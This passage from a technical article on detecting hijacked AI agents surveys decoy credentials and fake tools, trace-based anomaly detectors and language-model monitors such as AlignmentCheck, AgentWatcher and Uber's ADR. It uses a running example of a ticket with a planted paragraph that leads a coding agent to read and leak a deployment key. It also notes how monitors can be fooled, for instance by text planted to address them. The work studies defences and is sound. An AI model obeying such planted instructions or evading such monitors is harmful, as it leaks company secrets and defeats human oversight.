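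| Scanner | Missed: sending local files out | Missed: planting false records in memory | Harmless repositories flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| VirusTotal | 99% | 100% | 0% |
| Bandit | 13% | 3% | 63% |
| Semgrep | 60% | 58% | 17% |
| Tencent A.I.G | 49% | 77% | 38% |
| Cisco MCP Scanner | 20% | 100% | 0.6% |
| AntGroup MCPScan | 36% | 68% | 36% |
| All six combined | 8% | 3% | 66% |

VirusTotal, which combines many antivirus products, is good at recognising known malware, but this code was new. Bandit looks for insecure programming in general, and many of its detections probably had little to do with the attack. When Hu and colleagues tested the malicious code alone, Bandit missed all 100 of the file-encrypting tools. It missed only 31% of the real tools that contained such code, most likely because it flagged the harmless code around it.

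Of the six scanners, Cisco's, one of three designed for agent tools, is the most usable for detecting data theft. It caught 80% of the tools that sent local files out and raised very few false alarms, but it missed every tool that planted false records in an agent's memory. Combining all six scanners catches most attacks but flags two thirds of harmless repositories, too many for a reviewer to check. Given these results, it is sensible to scan for outgoing data before approving a tool, and then run the tool in a test environment to see which files and addresses it uses.

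### Tripwires

Unlike a rule, a tripwire can be set without a description of the attack, as long as it is somewhere no legitimate task should lead. A company can plant a fake password in a settings file, a fake payroll document in a shared folder, or a fake tool in the agent's list of tools. False alarms should be rare because nobody has a legitimate reason to use any of these.

Whether an attacker touches a decoy depends on its placement and realism. *Understanding and Evaluating Claw-like Agent Security Through a Computer-Systems Lens* (2026) puts decoys where real credentials would appear and gives them a different value for each test task, so that a leaked value identifies the task it came from. But its decoys begin with "CANARY", which would give them away in a real attack. *PHANTOM* (2026), a system for generating decoys, starts from the problem that credentials made from a template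 are easy to recognise, because they have generic user names and default settings instead of following the company's naming habits as real ones do.

Chauhan and Revankar (2026), in *Caught in the Act(ivation)*, give a formula for the chance of catching a thief who takes one credential at random:

P = k / (m + k) × (1 − β)

Here k is the number of decoys, m is the number of real credentials, and β is the chance that the monitor misses a decoy that leaks. With two real keys, three decoys and a β of 5%, P is 3/5 × 0.95, or 57%. But if the attacker can tell which keys are real, P falls to about zero. This makes decoys seriously weak against the ticket attack, where the attacker can name the deployment key in the planted paragraph. Decoys work better against an instruction to collect whatever passwords the agent can find.

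An agent that explores widely can set off a tripwire during legitimate work. If an employee asks it to find every file that mentions an old server, it may open the folder containing the fake password and read it. The team can allow for this by recording a read during a broad search as a low-priority note and raising an immediate alert if the agent sends the password somewhere or tries to log in with it.

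*Beyond Pattern Matching* (2026) states that any call to one of its detector's fake tools confirms an attack with 100% precision, because no harmless request leads to them. An experiment by Ghifiardi in *Optional Traps* (2026) suggests that legitimate agents can trigger decoys too, at least when the decoys are credentials. A legitimate agent had the correct key in its instructions but used a decoy key it found on a page meant for developers, and lost its access.

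In Ghifiardi's other tests, an agent played an outside intruder trying to export protected records. In the two sessions where the site leaked a working key and had decoys elsewhere, the agent took the working key and ignored the decoys. Ghifiardi then replaced the leaked key with a decoy, which the agent used in 19 of 20 sessions. Closing the leak without adding a decoy also stopped every theft, so the decoy served only to identify the intruder. The tests used only one simulated target and small models that can run on a single computer.

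Rassul and Rashid ran the largest test on hijacked agents, using AgentShield, which combines three fake tools and five fake credentials with a list of approved recipients, account numbers and web addresses. It caught 117 of 129 successful attacks on GPT-4o-mini and all 125 on GPT-5-mini. It raised no alarms in 485 harmless runs, but these were 97 tasks repeated five times each, so they cover less variety than 485 different tasks would. Elsewhere in the paper, Rassul and Rashid report much lower attack success rates, including zero for GPT-5-mini, so it is unclear what they counted as a successful attack.

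The decoys account for only part of these results. With GPT-4o-mini, the list of approved values raised 120 alerts and the fake tools raised 15; with GPT-5-mini, they raised 127 and 59. The fake credentials raised none in the standard tests because the agents never opened the files that held them. One fake tool was named "exfiltrate_data_to_attacker_server" so that no harmless agent would call it by accident, but a careful attacker would avoid it too.

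Some attackers can also learn to recognise decoys. *Say Shibboleth* (2026) cites a test in which an attacking agent identified 97% of open-source honeypots (entire decoy systems) when given a list of clues, and 19% without the list.

The evidence on decoys aimed at agents is thin, and none of these tests ran in a company's ordinary traffic. Tripwires are still worth trying because they are easy to plant and a team can measure their false alarms on its own agents. If 300 varied harmless sessions set off no tripwires, the true false-positive rate is probably below 1%.

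## Detecting attacks that no rule describes

Rules and tripwires raise an alert only if somebody has foreseen part of the attack. Suppose a comment planted in a shared code library leads a coding agent to weaken the company's login checks. The agent sends nothing to an outside address and touches no decoy, so neither the data-flow rule nor a fake password would catch it.

Two kinds of detector are meant to catch attacks that no rule describes. One learns from past sessions what an agent's work normally looks like. The other uses a language model to judge whether the agent's actions serve the user's request.

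### An old objection to learning what is normal

Long before AI agents, researchers built systems that learned a network's usual traffic and flagged departures from it, but few organisations relied on them, even though machine learning was doing well at jobs such as filtering spam. In *Outside the Closed World*, Sommer and Paxson (2010) attribute this partly to machine learning being best at recognising more of what it has already seen. A spam filter trains on both spam and ordinary mail, whereas an anomaly detector trains only on ordinary activity and treats everything else as suspect. This works only if the training data cover nearly everything ordinary.

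Sommer and Paxson also describe a "semantic gap". Such a detector finds unusual activity, but a security team needs to know whether the activity is an attack. Their other reasons are the serious consequences of errors, the diversity of network traffic, the difficulty of evaluating detectors, and attackers who adapt. Most of these reasons also apply to agents. For example, an agent's first session with a new supplier is unusual but almost always harmless.

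Lecture notes from Stanford that cite the paper suggest some remedies, including narrowing the detector's scope and sorting activity into known classes instead of searching for outliers. Both have been tried on agents.

### Order and meaning in TraceAegis

*TraceAegis* (Liu, Ruan and colleagues, 2025) covers only one agent with a fairly fixed workflow. Its detector needs only the tool calls with their inputs, outputs and order, which a gateway can record. It doesn't use the user's request or the agent's reasoning.

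Their main example is an agent that directs patients to hospital departments. It calls tool A1 to look up symptom keywords and A2 to analyse the patient's description, and then one tool for each department the patient should visit. TraceAegis learns from normal sessions as follows:

1. It gives each tool a level. A1 is on level 1, A2 on level 2 and all the departments on level 3. Tools that appear in either order in different sessions can share a level.
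2. It splits each session into short units that go down the levels. A1 → A2 → orthopaedics → psychiatry becomes A1 → A2 → orthopaedics and A1 → A2 → psychiatry.
3. A language model extracts a condition and an action from each unit, then merges units with the same tools. One patient with knee pain and another with arm pain produce the rule "knee pain or arm pain → orthopaedics".

The second step keeps the number of patterns manageable. With 18 departments, a patient who needs two could follow 18 × 17 = 306 different paths, but those paths contain only 18 different units.

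A new session P is normal only if it passes two checks:

Normal(P) = Struc(P) ∧ Sem(P)

Struc(P) holds if every unit in the session has occurred before, so it fails if the agent calls a department before A1. Sem(P) holds if the conditions fit, so it fails if a patient with foot pain is sent to ear, nose and throat, even though the order of the tools is familiar.

Liu and colleagues tested this on the hospital agent and on one that handles purchasing requests. They compared it with the same language models judging traces without the learned rules. The table gives F1 scores:

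| Language model | Hospital: model alone | Hospital: TraceAegis | Purchasing: model alone | Purchasing: TraceAegis |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Gemma-3-27B | 0.67 | 0.81 | 0.51 | 0.74 |
| GPT-OSS-120B | 0.87 | 0.95 | 0.65 | 0.94 |
| DeepSeek-V3 | 0.85 | 0.97 | 0.84 | 0.93 |

Among hospital sessions, TraceAegis with DeepSeek-V3 improved most over the model alone on those with a familiar order but the wrong content, catching 148 of 150 compared with 113. The reported scores imply about 10 false alarms on 300 harmless hospital sessions and about 21 on 300 purchasing sessions. Of the parts Liu and colleagues removed, splitting sessions into units lowered the hospital F1 score most, from 0.97 to 0.76. Removing the rules about conditions lowered it to 0.91.

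TraceAegis also flagged 132 of 140 crafted deviations in a technology company's agent that searches code for vulnerabilities. In one, a planted configuration file made the agent write its report before it had run the code to verify its findings. The agent's five stages normally run in a fixed order, so the reversal was easy to recognise.

TraceAegis would catch the ticket attack on an agent that only summarises tickets, because that agent never opens a private key in normal work and the attack would fail the order check. A coding assistant is much harder to cover, because the key repair has already produced the path from ticket to file to web, so the attack passes the order check. TraceAegis may also have learned that the assistant opens the key when a ticket concerns deployments, but the attacker wrote the ticket and can mention deployments in it. TraceAegis has no access to the employee's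 request, which was for a plain summary.

Mistakes in the training data are also hard to undo, because TraceAegis only adds to the relations it treats as normal. If the training sessions include an unnoticed attack, that attack's path will pass the order check from then on.

### Sessions as graphs

Zavrak (2026), in *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic*, used the other remedy, training classifiers on sessions labelled harmless or attacked. Zavrak represents each tool call as a node in a graph. One kind of edge joins consecutive calls, and another joins two calls if text from the start of the earlier call's result reappears in the later call's arguments.

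The ticket attack becomes three nodes in a row: the ticket read, the file read and the web call. In the sample trace, the recorder replaced the key with a short placeholder that appears in both the file result and the web call, so the graph also has a data-flow edge between those two nodes. Without the placeholder, the edge might be missing, because Zavrak's software skips results longer than 1,000 characters, and many private keys exceed that limit.

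Each node also needs a description in numbers. Zavrak compared two:

- Metadata consists of the tool's name, a hash of the arguments and the length of the result.
- Content consists of two embeddings, which are lists of 384 numbers that represent the meaning of a text. One covers the arguments and the other the result, each cut off after 512 characters. A planted paragraph at the end of a long ticket would therefore be left out.

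A graph neural network mixes each node's numbers with those of its neighbours, so the node for the web call also carries information about the file read before it. The network then combines all the nodes into one description of the session and scores it. The simpler models ignore the edges and take the average and the maximum of each embedding number over all the calls, which gives 1,536 numbers per session. They pass these to a classifier such as XGBoost, which adds up the outputs of many small decision trees.

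Zavrak's main dataset was RAS-Eval, with 605 harmless and 3,797 attacked sessions:

| Description | Model | AUROC |
|---|---|---|
| Metadata | Graph network (GraphSAGE) | 0.640 |
| Content | Graph network (GAT) | 0.891 |
| Content | Neural network without a graph | 0.896 |
| Content | Graph network (GraphSAGE) | 0.917 |
| Content | Logistic regression without a graph | 0.917 |
| Content | XGBoost without a graph | 0.975 |

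At its default threshold, XGBoost caught 92.7% of attacks and flagged 7.1% of harmless sessions. The graph added little, so a team that wants to try a trained classifier should probably start with decision trees.

The weak metadata result is partly due to the dataset. Attacks in RAS-Eval mostly change the arguments or results of calls, while the tools and their order stay much the same. *What Standard Evaluations Hide About Detectors of Hijacked LLM Agents* (Abbasi, Núñez V. and Shahraki, 2026) reports an AUROC of 0.936 on the synthetic dataset AgentDrift, using a model that reads only the sequence of tool names and ten simple measurements, such as the number of calls. But much of the signal in those measurements came from the length of the tool results, which differed between attacked and normal runs. That difference seems to come from how the dataset was generated.

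Test scores also depend heavily on how the data are divided. If sessions are assigned to training and test data at random, the same task appears in both. Because tasks use different tools, a model can then learn to recognise a task and how its sessions were labelled, without learning anything about attacks. The metadata model's AUROC was 0.898 with a random split, but 0.640 when Zavrak kept every test task out of the training data. The same change lowered a content model's score from 0.992 to 0.891. A team that tests a classifier on its own sessions should therefore hold out whole tasks.

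Even the better content scores should be read with caution. The attacked sessions in RAS-Eval all come from one language model and the harmless ones from eight, so a classifier may rely partly on the model's style. On ATBench, a second dataset with shorter sessions and subtler attacks, the best AUROC was 0.784. Attacks that changed only a tool's arguments were also hard to detect. In one test run, a graph network caught 37% of them, compared with 87% of those that changed both arguments and results.

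A bigger problem for finding new kinds of attack is that Zavrak held out tasks but not kinds of attack, so the results don't show how the classifiers would handle a kind missing from the training data. The classifiers also need labels. Zavrak tried training a network on harmless sessions before fine-tuning it on labelled ones, but this didn't reduce the number of labels needed. With 5% of the labels, the network scored 0.556, compared with 0.707 for one trained from scratch on the same labels.

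### Asking whether the actions serve the request

Neither TraceAegis nor Zavrak's classifiers use the user's request, which best separates the ticket attack from the key repair. A language-model monitor can compare the request with the agent's actions, and it needs no training on the company's own sessions.

Meta's *AlignmentCheck* describes one such monitor, which is part of LlamaFirewall. It is a prompt with a few worked examples, and any capable language model can run it. According to Abbasi and colleagues, the model receives the request together with every action up to that point, and has to judge whether the newest one serves some goal other than the user's. The software repeats this for every action and flags the session if it flags any step. For the ticket attack, the model would receive roughly this:

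```
request   "Summarise ticket 5831"
action 1  ticket.read   id=5831
action 2  file.read     path=deploy_key
```

A summary doesn't require a key, so the monitor can flag the session at action 2, before anything leaves the company. Meta's *LlamaFirewall Workflow and Detection Components* gives a similar example, in which a travel-planning agent reads a poisoned review site and starts to summarise the user's chat history instead of planning a beach trip. If AlignmentCheck detects the change of goal, it stops the agent from sending the summary. *LlamaFirewall* (Chennabasappa, Nikolaidis et al., 2025) describes this kind of check as "still experimental", although Meta uses LlamaFirewall in production.

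The prompt also has a field for the agent's stated reasoning, which is imperfect evidence. Abbasi and colleagues left this field empty in their tests.

OpenAI's *Prompt Injection Detection* describes a comparable check, which runs before each tool call and again on each result. With its default model, the check caught 98.6% of attacks at a false-positive rate of 1%. Half of the 1,000 test conversations were attacks, and the published examples are easy, such as an agent that is asked to schedule a meeting and also looks up bank accounts. The smallest model in the test had an AUROC of 0.943 but caught no attacks at the same false-positive rate.

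### AlignmentCheck on AgentDojo

Most monitors of this kind have been tested on AgentDojo. It gives an agent tasks in four simulated settings (an office workspace, travel, banking and Slack), plants instructions in the tool results, and checks automatically whether the agent carried out the attacker's goal. Abbasi and colleagues took recorded AgentDojo sessions from five agent models, 2,294 of them hijacked and 392 harmless, and ran AlignmentCheck on them with two different language models. They also ran it on 4,987 sessions in which the attack had failed:

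| Model running AlignmentCheck | Hijacked sessions flagged | Harmless sessions flagged | Failed attacks flagged |
|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 90.0% | 17.3% | 21.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 88.3% | 3.8% | 6.3% |

The choice of model had little effect on recall but a large effect on false alarms. Claude is not always the better choice, because on AgentDrift it flagged 31.3% of the sessions without an attack, compared with 22.1% for Llama. Many of those sessions were deliberately difficult.

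AlignmentCheck, using Llama, had an AUROC of 0.930 on AgentDojo. Classifiers that Abbasi and colleagues trained on AgentDrift scored between 0.47 and 0.52 on the same sessions, which is no better than guessing. A team with no labelled attacks on its own agents should therefore try a language-model monitor before a trained classifier. The comparison may somewhat overstate AlignmentCheck's advantage, since Meta also evaluated its prompt on AgentDojo.

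AgentDojo has another weakness as a test. Five fixed attack strings appear in 99.6% of the hijacked sessions and in none of the harmless ones, so a plain text search for them reaches an AUROC of 0.998. Detectors that read tool results can benefit from these strings, which makes their AgentDojo scores harder to interpret. This doesn't affect AlignmentCheck, because its prompt contains no tool results.

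AlignmentCheck relies heavily on tool names. When Abbasi and colleagues hid the tool names in AgentDrift, AlignmentCheck's AUROC fell from 0.856 to 0.765. A malicious tool with an innocent name would probably weaken it too.

### How much untrusted text to show the monitor

Leaving tool results out of the monitor's input protects it from text planted in them. The monitor is a language model, like the agent, so an attacker could plant text that addresses it directly. The protection is incomplete because the agent may copy planted text into the arguments of a call, which the monitor does read.

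But the results may also contain the reason for a legitimate action. In the key repair, the employee asks the agent to resolve a ticket, and only the ticket mentions failed deployments. Without the ticket's text, the monitor has only a vague request followed by the agent opening a private key, and could reasonably flag it. The same happens when a user asks an agent to carry out the tasks in a colleague's email, because the monitor has no record of those tasks.

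Wang, Zou and colleagues (2026), in *AgentWatcher*, offer a compromise, which is to show the monitor only the untrusted text that seems to have influenced the action. They find this text with attention weights, numbers inside a language model that indicate how strongly one piece of text affects the processing of another:

1. A language model processes the request, the untrusted text and the agent's action. For each token (a word or part of a word) at position j in the untrusted text, the software averages the attention that the tokens of the action give it. Call this average A(j).
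2. The software scores every run of ten tokens with S(i) = (A(i) + A(i+1) + … + A(i+9)) / 10.
3. It takes the run with the highest score together with the 150 tokens before it and the 50 after it, which makes 210 tokens. It does this three times without overlap, so the monitor receives at most 630 tokens of untrusted text.
4. A second language model gets this text, a short version of the user's task, the action and a list of written rules about what counts as an injection. It gives a brief explanation and a verdict, and quotes the injection if it finds one.

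For the ticket attack, the action would be the file read, and the highest-scoring run of text should fall in the planted paragraph. If the agent uses a closed model, its attention weights aren't available, so a separate open model has to supply them. The selected text is then what influenced the open model, which may not be what influenced the agent.

On AgentDojo, with GPT-4o-mini as the agent, AgentWatcher cut the success rate of attacks from 22% to 1% or less, while the share of tasks the agent completed when there was no attack fell from 73% to 71%. But the monitor did almost as well there when it was given all the untrusted text instead of a selection. Selecting text helped more on long code files, where it cut the success rate of one attack from 10% to 3%. On AgentDyn, a harder set of tasks, no attack succeeded, but the agent completed only 48.3% of its tasks. Wang and colleagues acknowledge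 that harmless instructions can be very hard to tell from malicious ones.

Teams can add their own rules, but they have to be careful with exceptions. Wang and colleagues suggest, for example, that if a user asks the agent to read an email from Alice, the monitor should treat any instructions in that email as harmless. The same exception for tickets would let the ticket attack through, because the planted paragraph is in the ticket the employee named.

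AgentWatcher also differs slightly from AlignmentCheck in that it checks whether the text contains an injection. In one of its published examples, it flags an instruction to transfer money although the agent's next action was a harmless date lookup. A team can learn from such alerts that somebody is trying to attack its agents, but should keep them in a separate queue from alerts about hijacked sessions.

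Each check takes 8.2 seconds on average, so Wang and colleagues recommend running it only before risky actions, such as shell commands or access to credentials. Used this way, the method depends partly on a list of risky actions, and an attack that uses only unlisted actions would go unchecked.

### Uber's two-stage detector

Uber's ADR system also checks actions against the request, but it can look up additional evidence before deciding. Checking every session thoroughly would be expensive, so Li and colleagues divided the work into two stages.

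The screening stage uses a single prompt to a language model, which was GPT-4o in the tests. The model checks for phrases typical of prompt injection, requests that involve credentials or permissions, changes of role, and steps that are harmless alone but risky together. The screening stage closes sessions that are clearly harmless and sends any doubtful ones to the next stage.

The investigation stage is itself an agent, which ran on Claude Sonnet 4. It can use three sources:

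- The source code of a tool shows what the tool actually does.
- Threat intelligence describes known attack methods and what to look for.
- Company policy shows whether an action breaks a rule, even if nobody attacked the agent.

The agent chooses which sources to consult. For the ticket attack, it might look up the guidance on injections in external text and the policy on private keys. For a wallpaper tool that secretly uploads documents, the trace may look normal, so the source code would be the best evidence.

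Li and colleagues compared ADR with three other detectors on their own 302 tasks and on 93 tasks from AgentDojo. ALRPHFS matches sessions against 301 stored attack patterns and asks a language model about unclear cases. GuardAgent checks actions against 47 security policies. Li and colleagues describe LlamaFirewall as a prompt classifier with some simple rules and don't mention AlignmentCheck, so LlamaFirewall's poor result is probably weak evidence of how well AlignmentCheck works.

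| Detector | Own test: attacks caught (of 42) | Own test: false alarms (of 260) | Own test: cost per task | AgentDojo: attacks caught (of 38) | AgentDojo: false alarms (of 55) |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| ADR | 28 | 0 | $0.024 | 38 | 3 |
| ALRPHFS | 17 | 34 | $0.001 | 32 | 3 |
| GuardAgent | 9 | 30 | $0.012 | 27 | 8 |
| LlamaFirewall | 8 | 40 | $0.459 | 37 | 21 |

ADR has a large lead on Li and colleagues' own test and a smaller one on AgentDojo. The difference may be partly because they designed both the detector and the test using the same list of 17 attack techniques. ADR raised no false alarms in 260 tasks, but its true false-alarm rate could still be as high as about 1%. ADR might do better with newer language models, since both of the ones it uses are now old.

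Recall was 1 of 5 for permission abuse and 5 of 5 for security control bypass, but such differences between tactics are less reliable than they look, because even 5 of 5 is compatible with a true recall of about 50%.

To find out which parts mattered, Li and colleagues removed them one at a time. They report recall and F1 scores, from which the number of false alarms follows:

| Part removed | Recall | False alarms |
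|---|---|---|
| None | 0.667 | 0 |
| Source code | 0.571 | 5 |
| Threat intelligence | 0.585 | 2 |
| Company policy | 0.675 | 0 |
| Screening stage | 0.805 | 2 |

The recall of 0.805 without screening doesn't correspond to a whole number of detected attacks out of 42. It does match 33 out of 41, so one attack may be missing from that run. The figures without threat intelligence and without policy have the same problem. The results still show fairly clearly that source code and threat intelligence help and that screening causes some attacks to be missed.

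Source code seems to help ADR, which missed more attacks and raised more false alarms without it. The policy lookup made almost no difference, which is surprising given ADR's poor result on permission abuse, where knowing what an agent is allowed to do should matter most. Li and colleagues suggest that most attacks in the test break obvious security principles, which a language model can recognise without a written policy.

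### Why two stages lose attacks

ADR catches an attack only if both stages get it right. If screening passes on a share r₁ of the attacks, and the investigation recognises a share r₂ of those, then

recall = r₁ × r₂

Suppose there are 100 attacks. Screening forwards 90 of them to the investigation, which recognises 80% of those, so ADR catches 72. Even a perfect investigation would catch only 90, because it never receives the other 10.

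In Li and colleagues' tests, the full system caught 28 attacks and the investigation stage alone apparently caught 33. Screening therefore missed about five attacks, or 15% of those the investigation would have caught, although the true loss could be somewhat different because a language model's verdicts vary between runs.

Screening is probably most likely to miss new kinds of attack, because the prompt describes known warning signs, as a rule would. An attack with none of those signs may never reach the stage that could have checked a tool's source code.

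One remedy is to add a second way for sessions to reach the investigation. Suppose the data-flow rule catches 60% of attacks and its misses are independent of the screening prompt's. If either one can pass a session on, together they miss only 0.1 × 0.4 = 4% of attacks, and recall rises from 72% to 0.96 × 0.8 = 77%. If the rule only catches attacks that screening would have passed on anyway, recall doesn't improve. A team can check for this overlap by running staged attacks through the screening stage alone and examining the ones it closes.

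A company could also drop screening and investigate everything. Screening closed 40.7% of the tasks by itself, in 2.3 seconds on average, compared with 29.7 seconds for tasks that went on to investigation. Without it, the average cost rose from $0.024 to $0.031 per task. At Uber's volume of 10,000 sessions a day, that would add about $70 a day, if real sessions cost the same as the test tasks. The extra false alarms would cost more than that because analysts would have to check them. There were two in 260 harmless tasks, and at that rate 10,000 harmless sessions a day would produce about 77.

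## Working out how many alerts will be real

When attacks are rare, even a 1% false-positive rate can fill an analyst's queue with false alarms. Suppose a company's agents run 10,000 sessions a day and attackers hijack 10 of them. A detector with 90% recall and a 1% false-positive rate will raise 10 × 0.90 = 9 real alerts and 9,990 × 0.01 ≈ 100 false ones. Its precision is 9/109, or about 8%.

The same steps give a general formula. Call the prevalence π, the recall R and the false-positive rate F. Out of N sessions, πN contain an attack, and the detector catches πNR of those. The other (1 − π)N are harmless, and the detector flags (1 − π)NF of them. N cancels out:

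precision = πR / (πR + (1 − π)F)

Half of the alerts are real when the two terms in the denominator are equal, which happens when F = πR / (1 − π). In the example, this is 0.001 × 0.9 / 0.999, or about 0.09%, so the false-positive rate has to fall to about an eleventh of its current level. Better recall would hardly help. Catching all 10 attacks at the same false-positive rate would raise precision only to 9%, whereas halving the false-positive rate would raise it to 15%.

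A company doesn't know in advance how many of its sessions attackers will hijack, so it makes sense to try several values:

| Attacked sessions per 10,000 | Real alerts | False alerts | Precision | False-positive rate at which half the alerts are real |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 100 | 90 | 99 | 48% | 0.9% |
| 10 | 9 | 100 | 8% | 0.09% |
| 1 | 0.9 | 100 | 0.9% | 0.009% |

Conventional security teams already face figures like those in the bottom row, or worse. *AI-Driven Security Alert Screening and Alert Fatigue Mitigation in Security Operations Centers* (2026), a survey, cites one large operation where only about 0.01% of daily alerts were linked to a real attack.

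### Axelsson's argument

The formula comes from Bayes' theorem. Axelsson (2000) used it in *The Base-Rate Fallacy and the Difficulty of Intrusion Detection* to argue that the main limit on an intrusion detector is how well it suppresses false alarms, not how well it recognises intrusions. The base-rate fallacy is people's habit of ignoring how rare something is when they interpret a positive test for it.

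Axelsson imagined a small site with a few dozen users, a million log records a day and two intrusions, each affecting ten records. Even if a detector caught every intrusion, it would need a false-alarm rate of about 1 in 100,000 for two thirds of its alarms to be real. If the site tolerated 100 false alarms a day, only about 2% of its alarms would be real.

The argument also depends on how people react to false alarms. Axelsson had no experiments on security staff to draw on, so he relied on studies of people who run power stations, paper mills and ships. These suggested that most operators stop trusting an alarm by the time half of its warnings are false.

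For Anthropic's *Auto mode is now the default in Claude Code* (2026), a research vendor had 1,053 paid testers use a coding agent that repeatedly asked for permission to run commands. The vendor replaced one request with a clearly dangerous one. Testers refused it about 17% of the time early in a session and about 5% of the time after 50 or more requests. Anthropic was arguing for replacing these requests with a classifier, and the testers had no projects of their own at stake. A professional alert analyst should do better than 17%, but the decline fits Axelsson's worry that frequent false alarms teach people to stop looking.

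### No false alarms in 260 tasks

Uber's detector raised no false alarms on the 260 harmless tasks in its own test, but its false-positive rate may still be above zero. If the rate is F, the chance of no false alarms in 260 tasks is (1 − F)^260. That chance falls to 5% when F is about 1.15%, so the test rules out higher rates with 95% confidence but is compatible with any lower rate.

At a false positive rate of 1.15%, the company in the example would get about 115 false alerts a day. With the 67% recall that Li and colleagues measured, it would also get about 7 real ones, for a precision of 5.5%. But the actual false positive rate could also be close to zero, in which case nearly every alert would be real. The test is too small to show which of these a company should expect.

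To show that the false alarm rate is below 0.09%, a team would need about 3,300 harmless sessions without a false alarm, which is a third of a day's traffic in the example. Since nearly all real sessions are harmless, the team only has to check the few that raise an alert. Recall is much harder to measure because real attacks are scarce. If a monitor catches 28 of 42 attacks, the 95% interval for its recall runs from about 52% to 79%.

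The 1.15% bound also holds only for sessions like those in the test. Li and colleagues had GPT-4 write some of the harmless tasks as variations on existing ones, and a company's real sessions may well be messier.

### Tests with too many attacks

Attacks usually make up a far larger share of published tests than of real traffic. Abbasi and colleagues audited eleven evaluations of detectors that read agents' traces. In the test sets that also included normal sessions, between 16% and 86% of sessions were attacked or anomalous. None of the eleven varied that share, and only four reported a measure that doesn't depend on a single threshold, such as AUROC.

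Precision measured on a test set with many attacks overstates the precision to expect when attacks are rare. Zavrak's best classifier caught 92.7% of attacks and flagged 7.1% of harmless sessions. These rates imply a precision of about 99% with 86% attacks, as in that test, but 1.3% with 10 attacks in 10,000 sessions. *Structural Baselines Matter for Agent Failure Detection and Attribution* (2026) acknowledges the same problem in its own results on detecting agents that fail at their tasks. Its detectors had a precision of 97% to 99% on a test set with 87% failures, a rate that "no real deployment matches".

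Abbasi and colleagues then tested several detectors on AgentDrift, the synthetic dataset, and calculated what would happen if attackers had hijacked 2% of sessions. They set the trained detectors' thresholds to flag 80% of the attacked sessions in the training data, and used AlignmentCheck's own yes-or-no decision:

| Detector | AUROC | Recall | False-positive rate | Precision at 2% | Alerts per 1,000 sessions |
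|---|---|---|---|---|---|
| Logistic regression on tool counts and behaviour | 0.879 | 77% | 19% | 7.6% | 203 |
| Neural network on the sequence of tools | 0.936 | 68% | 4.5% | 24% | 58 |
| Word-frequency classifier on the full text | 0.999 | 76% | 0% | 100% | 15 |
| AlignmentCheck with Llama 3.3 70B | 0.856 | 85% | 22% | 7.3% | 233 |
| AlignmentCheck with Claude Sonnet 5.5 | 0.817 | 87% | 31% | 5.4% | 324 |

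The logistic regression has a respectable-looking AUROC of 0.879, but it raises 12 false alerts for every real one. At a prevalence of 0.1%, its precision falls to 0.4%, or about 250 false alerts for each real one.

The word-frequency classifier is the exception, but it had mostly learned patterns from how the dataset's makers generated the sessions. For example, the text "2026" appears in 74% of the ordinary harmless training sessions but only 5% of the attacked ones. On AgentDojo, the classifier ranked sessions no better than chance and flagged none of them.

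Precision also depends on what kind of harmless sessions a company has. The logistic regression flagged 12% of AgentDrift's ordinary harmless sessions but 39% of those designed to be difficult. At a prevalence of 2%, precision would be 11.7% if every harmless session were ordinary and 3.9% if every one were difficult. A team whose agents repair keys and deployments all day should expect precision near the lower figure, even if its attack rate is the same as other teams'.

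### Tools the detector has never met

Companies keep connecting their agents to new tools, and some detectors cope badly with this. To measure the effect, Abbasi and colleagues hid a growing share of the tool names in the AgentDrift test sessions, so that the detectors treated those tools as unknown. They kept the thresholds the same:

| Detector | AUROC, all tools familiar | AUROC, none familiar | False-positive rate, all familiar | False-positive rate, none familiar |
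|---|---|---|---|---|
| Logistic regression on behaviour only | 0.830 | 0.830 | 28% | 28% |
| Logistic regression on tool counts and behaviour | 0.879 | 0.787 | 19% | 66% |
| Neural network on the sequence of tools | 0.936 | 0.674 | 4.5% | 74% |

The detector that ranks best when the tools are familiar ranks worst when none of them are. It loses its advantage when the share of tool calls that use familiar tools falls to somewhere between 78% and 48%, so a company can lose that advantage by replacing only some of its tools. In a company with 10,000 harmless sessions a day, the neural network's false alerts would rise from 450 to about 7,400.

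The neural network fails because it replaces every unfamiliar tool name with a single "unknown" symbol. That symbol never appeared in training, so the network's response to it was arbitrary and made harmless sessions look more like attacks. Abbasi and colleagues largely fixed this by randomly replacing 20% of the tool names with the symbol during training. The false-positive rate then stayed between 5% and 7% at every level of familiarity, and AUROC fell only to 0.794.

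Thresholds can fail for other reasons too. Another detector represented each step by its meaning, so it could handle new tool names. But when Abbasi and colleagues tested it on a kind of work they had left out of training, such as web browsing, its false-positive rate rose from 0.1% to as much as 10.6%.

A team can bring the number of alerts back down without labelling any sessions, by moving the threshold until the detector flags the usual share of them. Abbasi and colleagues tried this with 200 unlabelled sessions. The neural network's recall then dropped to between 12% and 27%, because a new threshold doesn't improve the order in which a detector ranks sessions.

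Hiding names is a harsher test than most companies will face. In recorded AgentDojo sessions, leaving out one of the four settings at a time didn't consistently reverse the ranking of the two logistic regressions. Still, companies that add a batch of new tools have good reason to measure the false-positive rate again.

### A second benchmark

Detectors trained on AgentDrift had an AUROC of only 0.47 to 0.52 on AgentDojo. With its threshold unchanged, the logistic regression on tool counts and behaviour flagged 22.4% of harmless sessions and 22.5% of hijacked ones, so its alerts were no better than picking sessions at random. The same types of detector scored between 0.74 and 0.996 when trained on other AgentDojo tasks, so the hijacked sessions were detectable. The two datasets differ in their tools, attacks, labels and origin, and Abbasi and colleagues can't say which difference caused the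 failure.

AlignmentCheck did much better on AgentDojo, but at a 2% attack rate its precision with Llama would still be only 9.6%. With Claude Sonnet 5.5 it would be 32%, though the interval runs from 20% to 59%, and the same setup would reach only 5.4% on AgentDrift. Even 32% precision means about two false alerts for every real one, and the true attack rate may be much lower than 2%. At 0.1%, the same AgentDojo results for Claude would give a precision of 2.3%.

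Abbasi and colleagues recommend that anyone who evaluates such a detector should:

1. report AUROC together with precision at a fixed threshold, for stated attack rates such as 1% to 10%
2. describe the harmless sessions and give the false-positive rate for each kind
3. report what share of the tool calls in the test use familiar tools, and include a test where many don't
4. set the threshold without using test data, and train detectors that use tool names to handle missing ones
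5. compare the detector with a simple text classifier, and change any cue that an attacker controls
6. when testing on a second dataset, also train the same type of detector on that dataset, to find out whether the task can be learned there
7. hold ready-made monitors to the same standard.

A security team can use this list to question a vendor. The second and third points are probably the most revealing, because a vendor can calculate precision for any attack rate but can't guess how the detector will treat a customer's own tools and difficult sessions.

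### Uber's alerts in production

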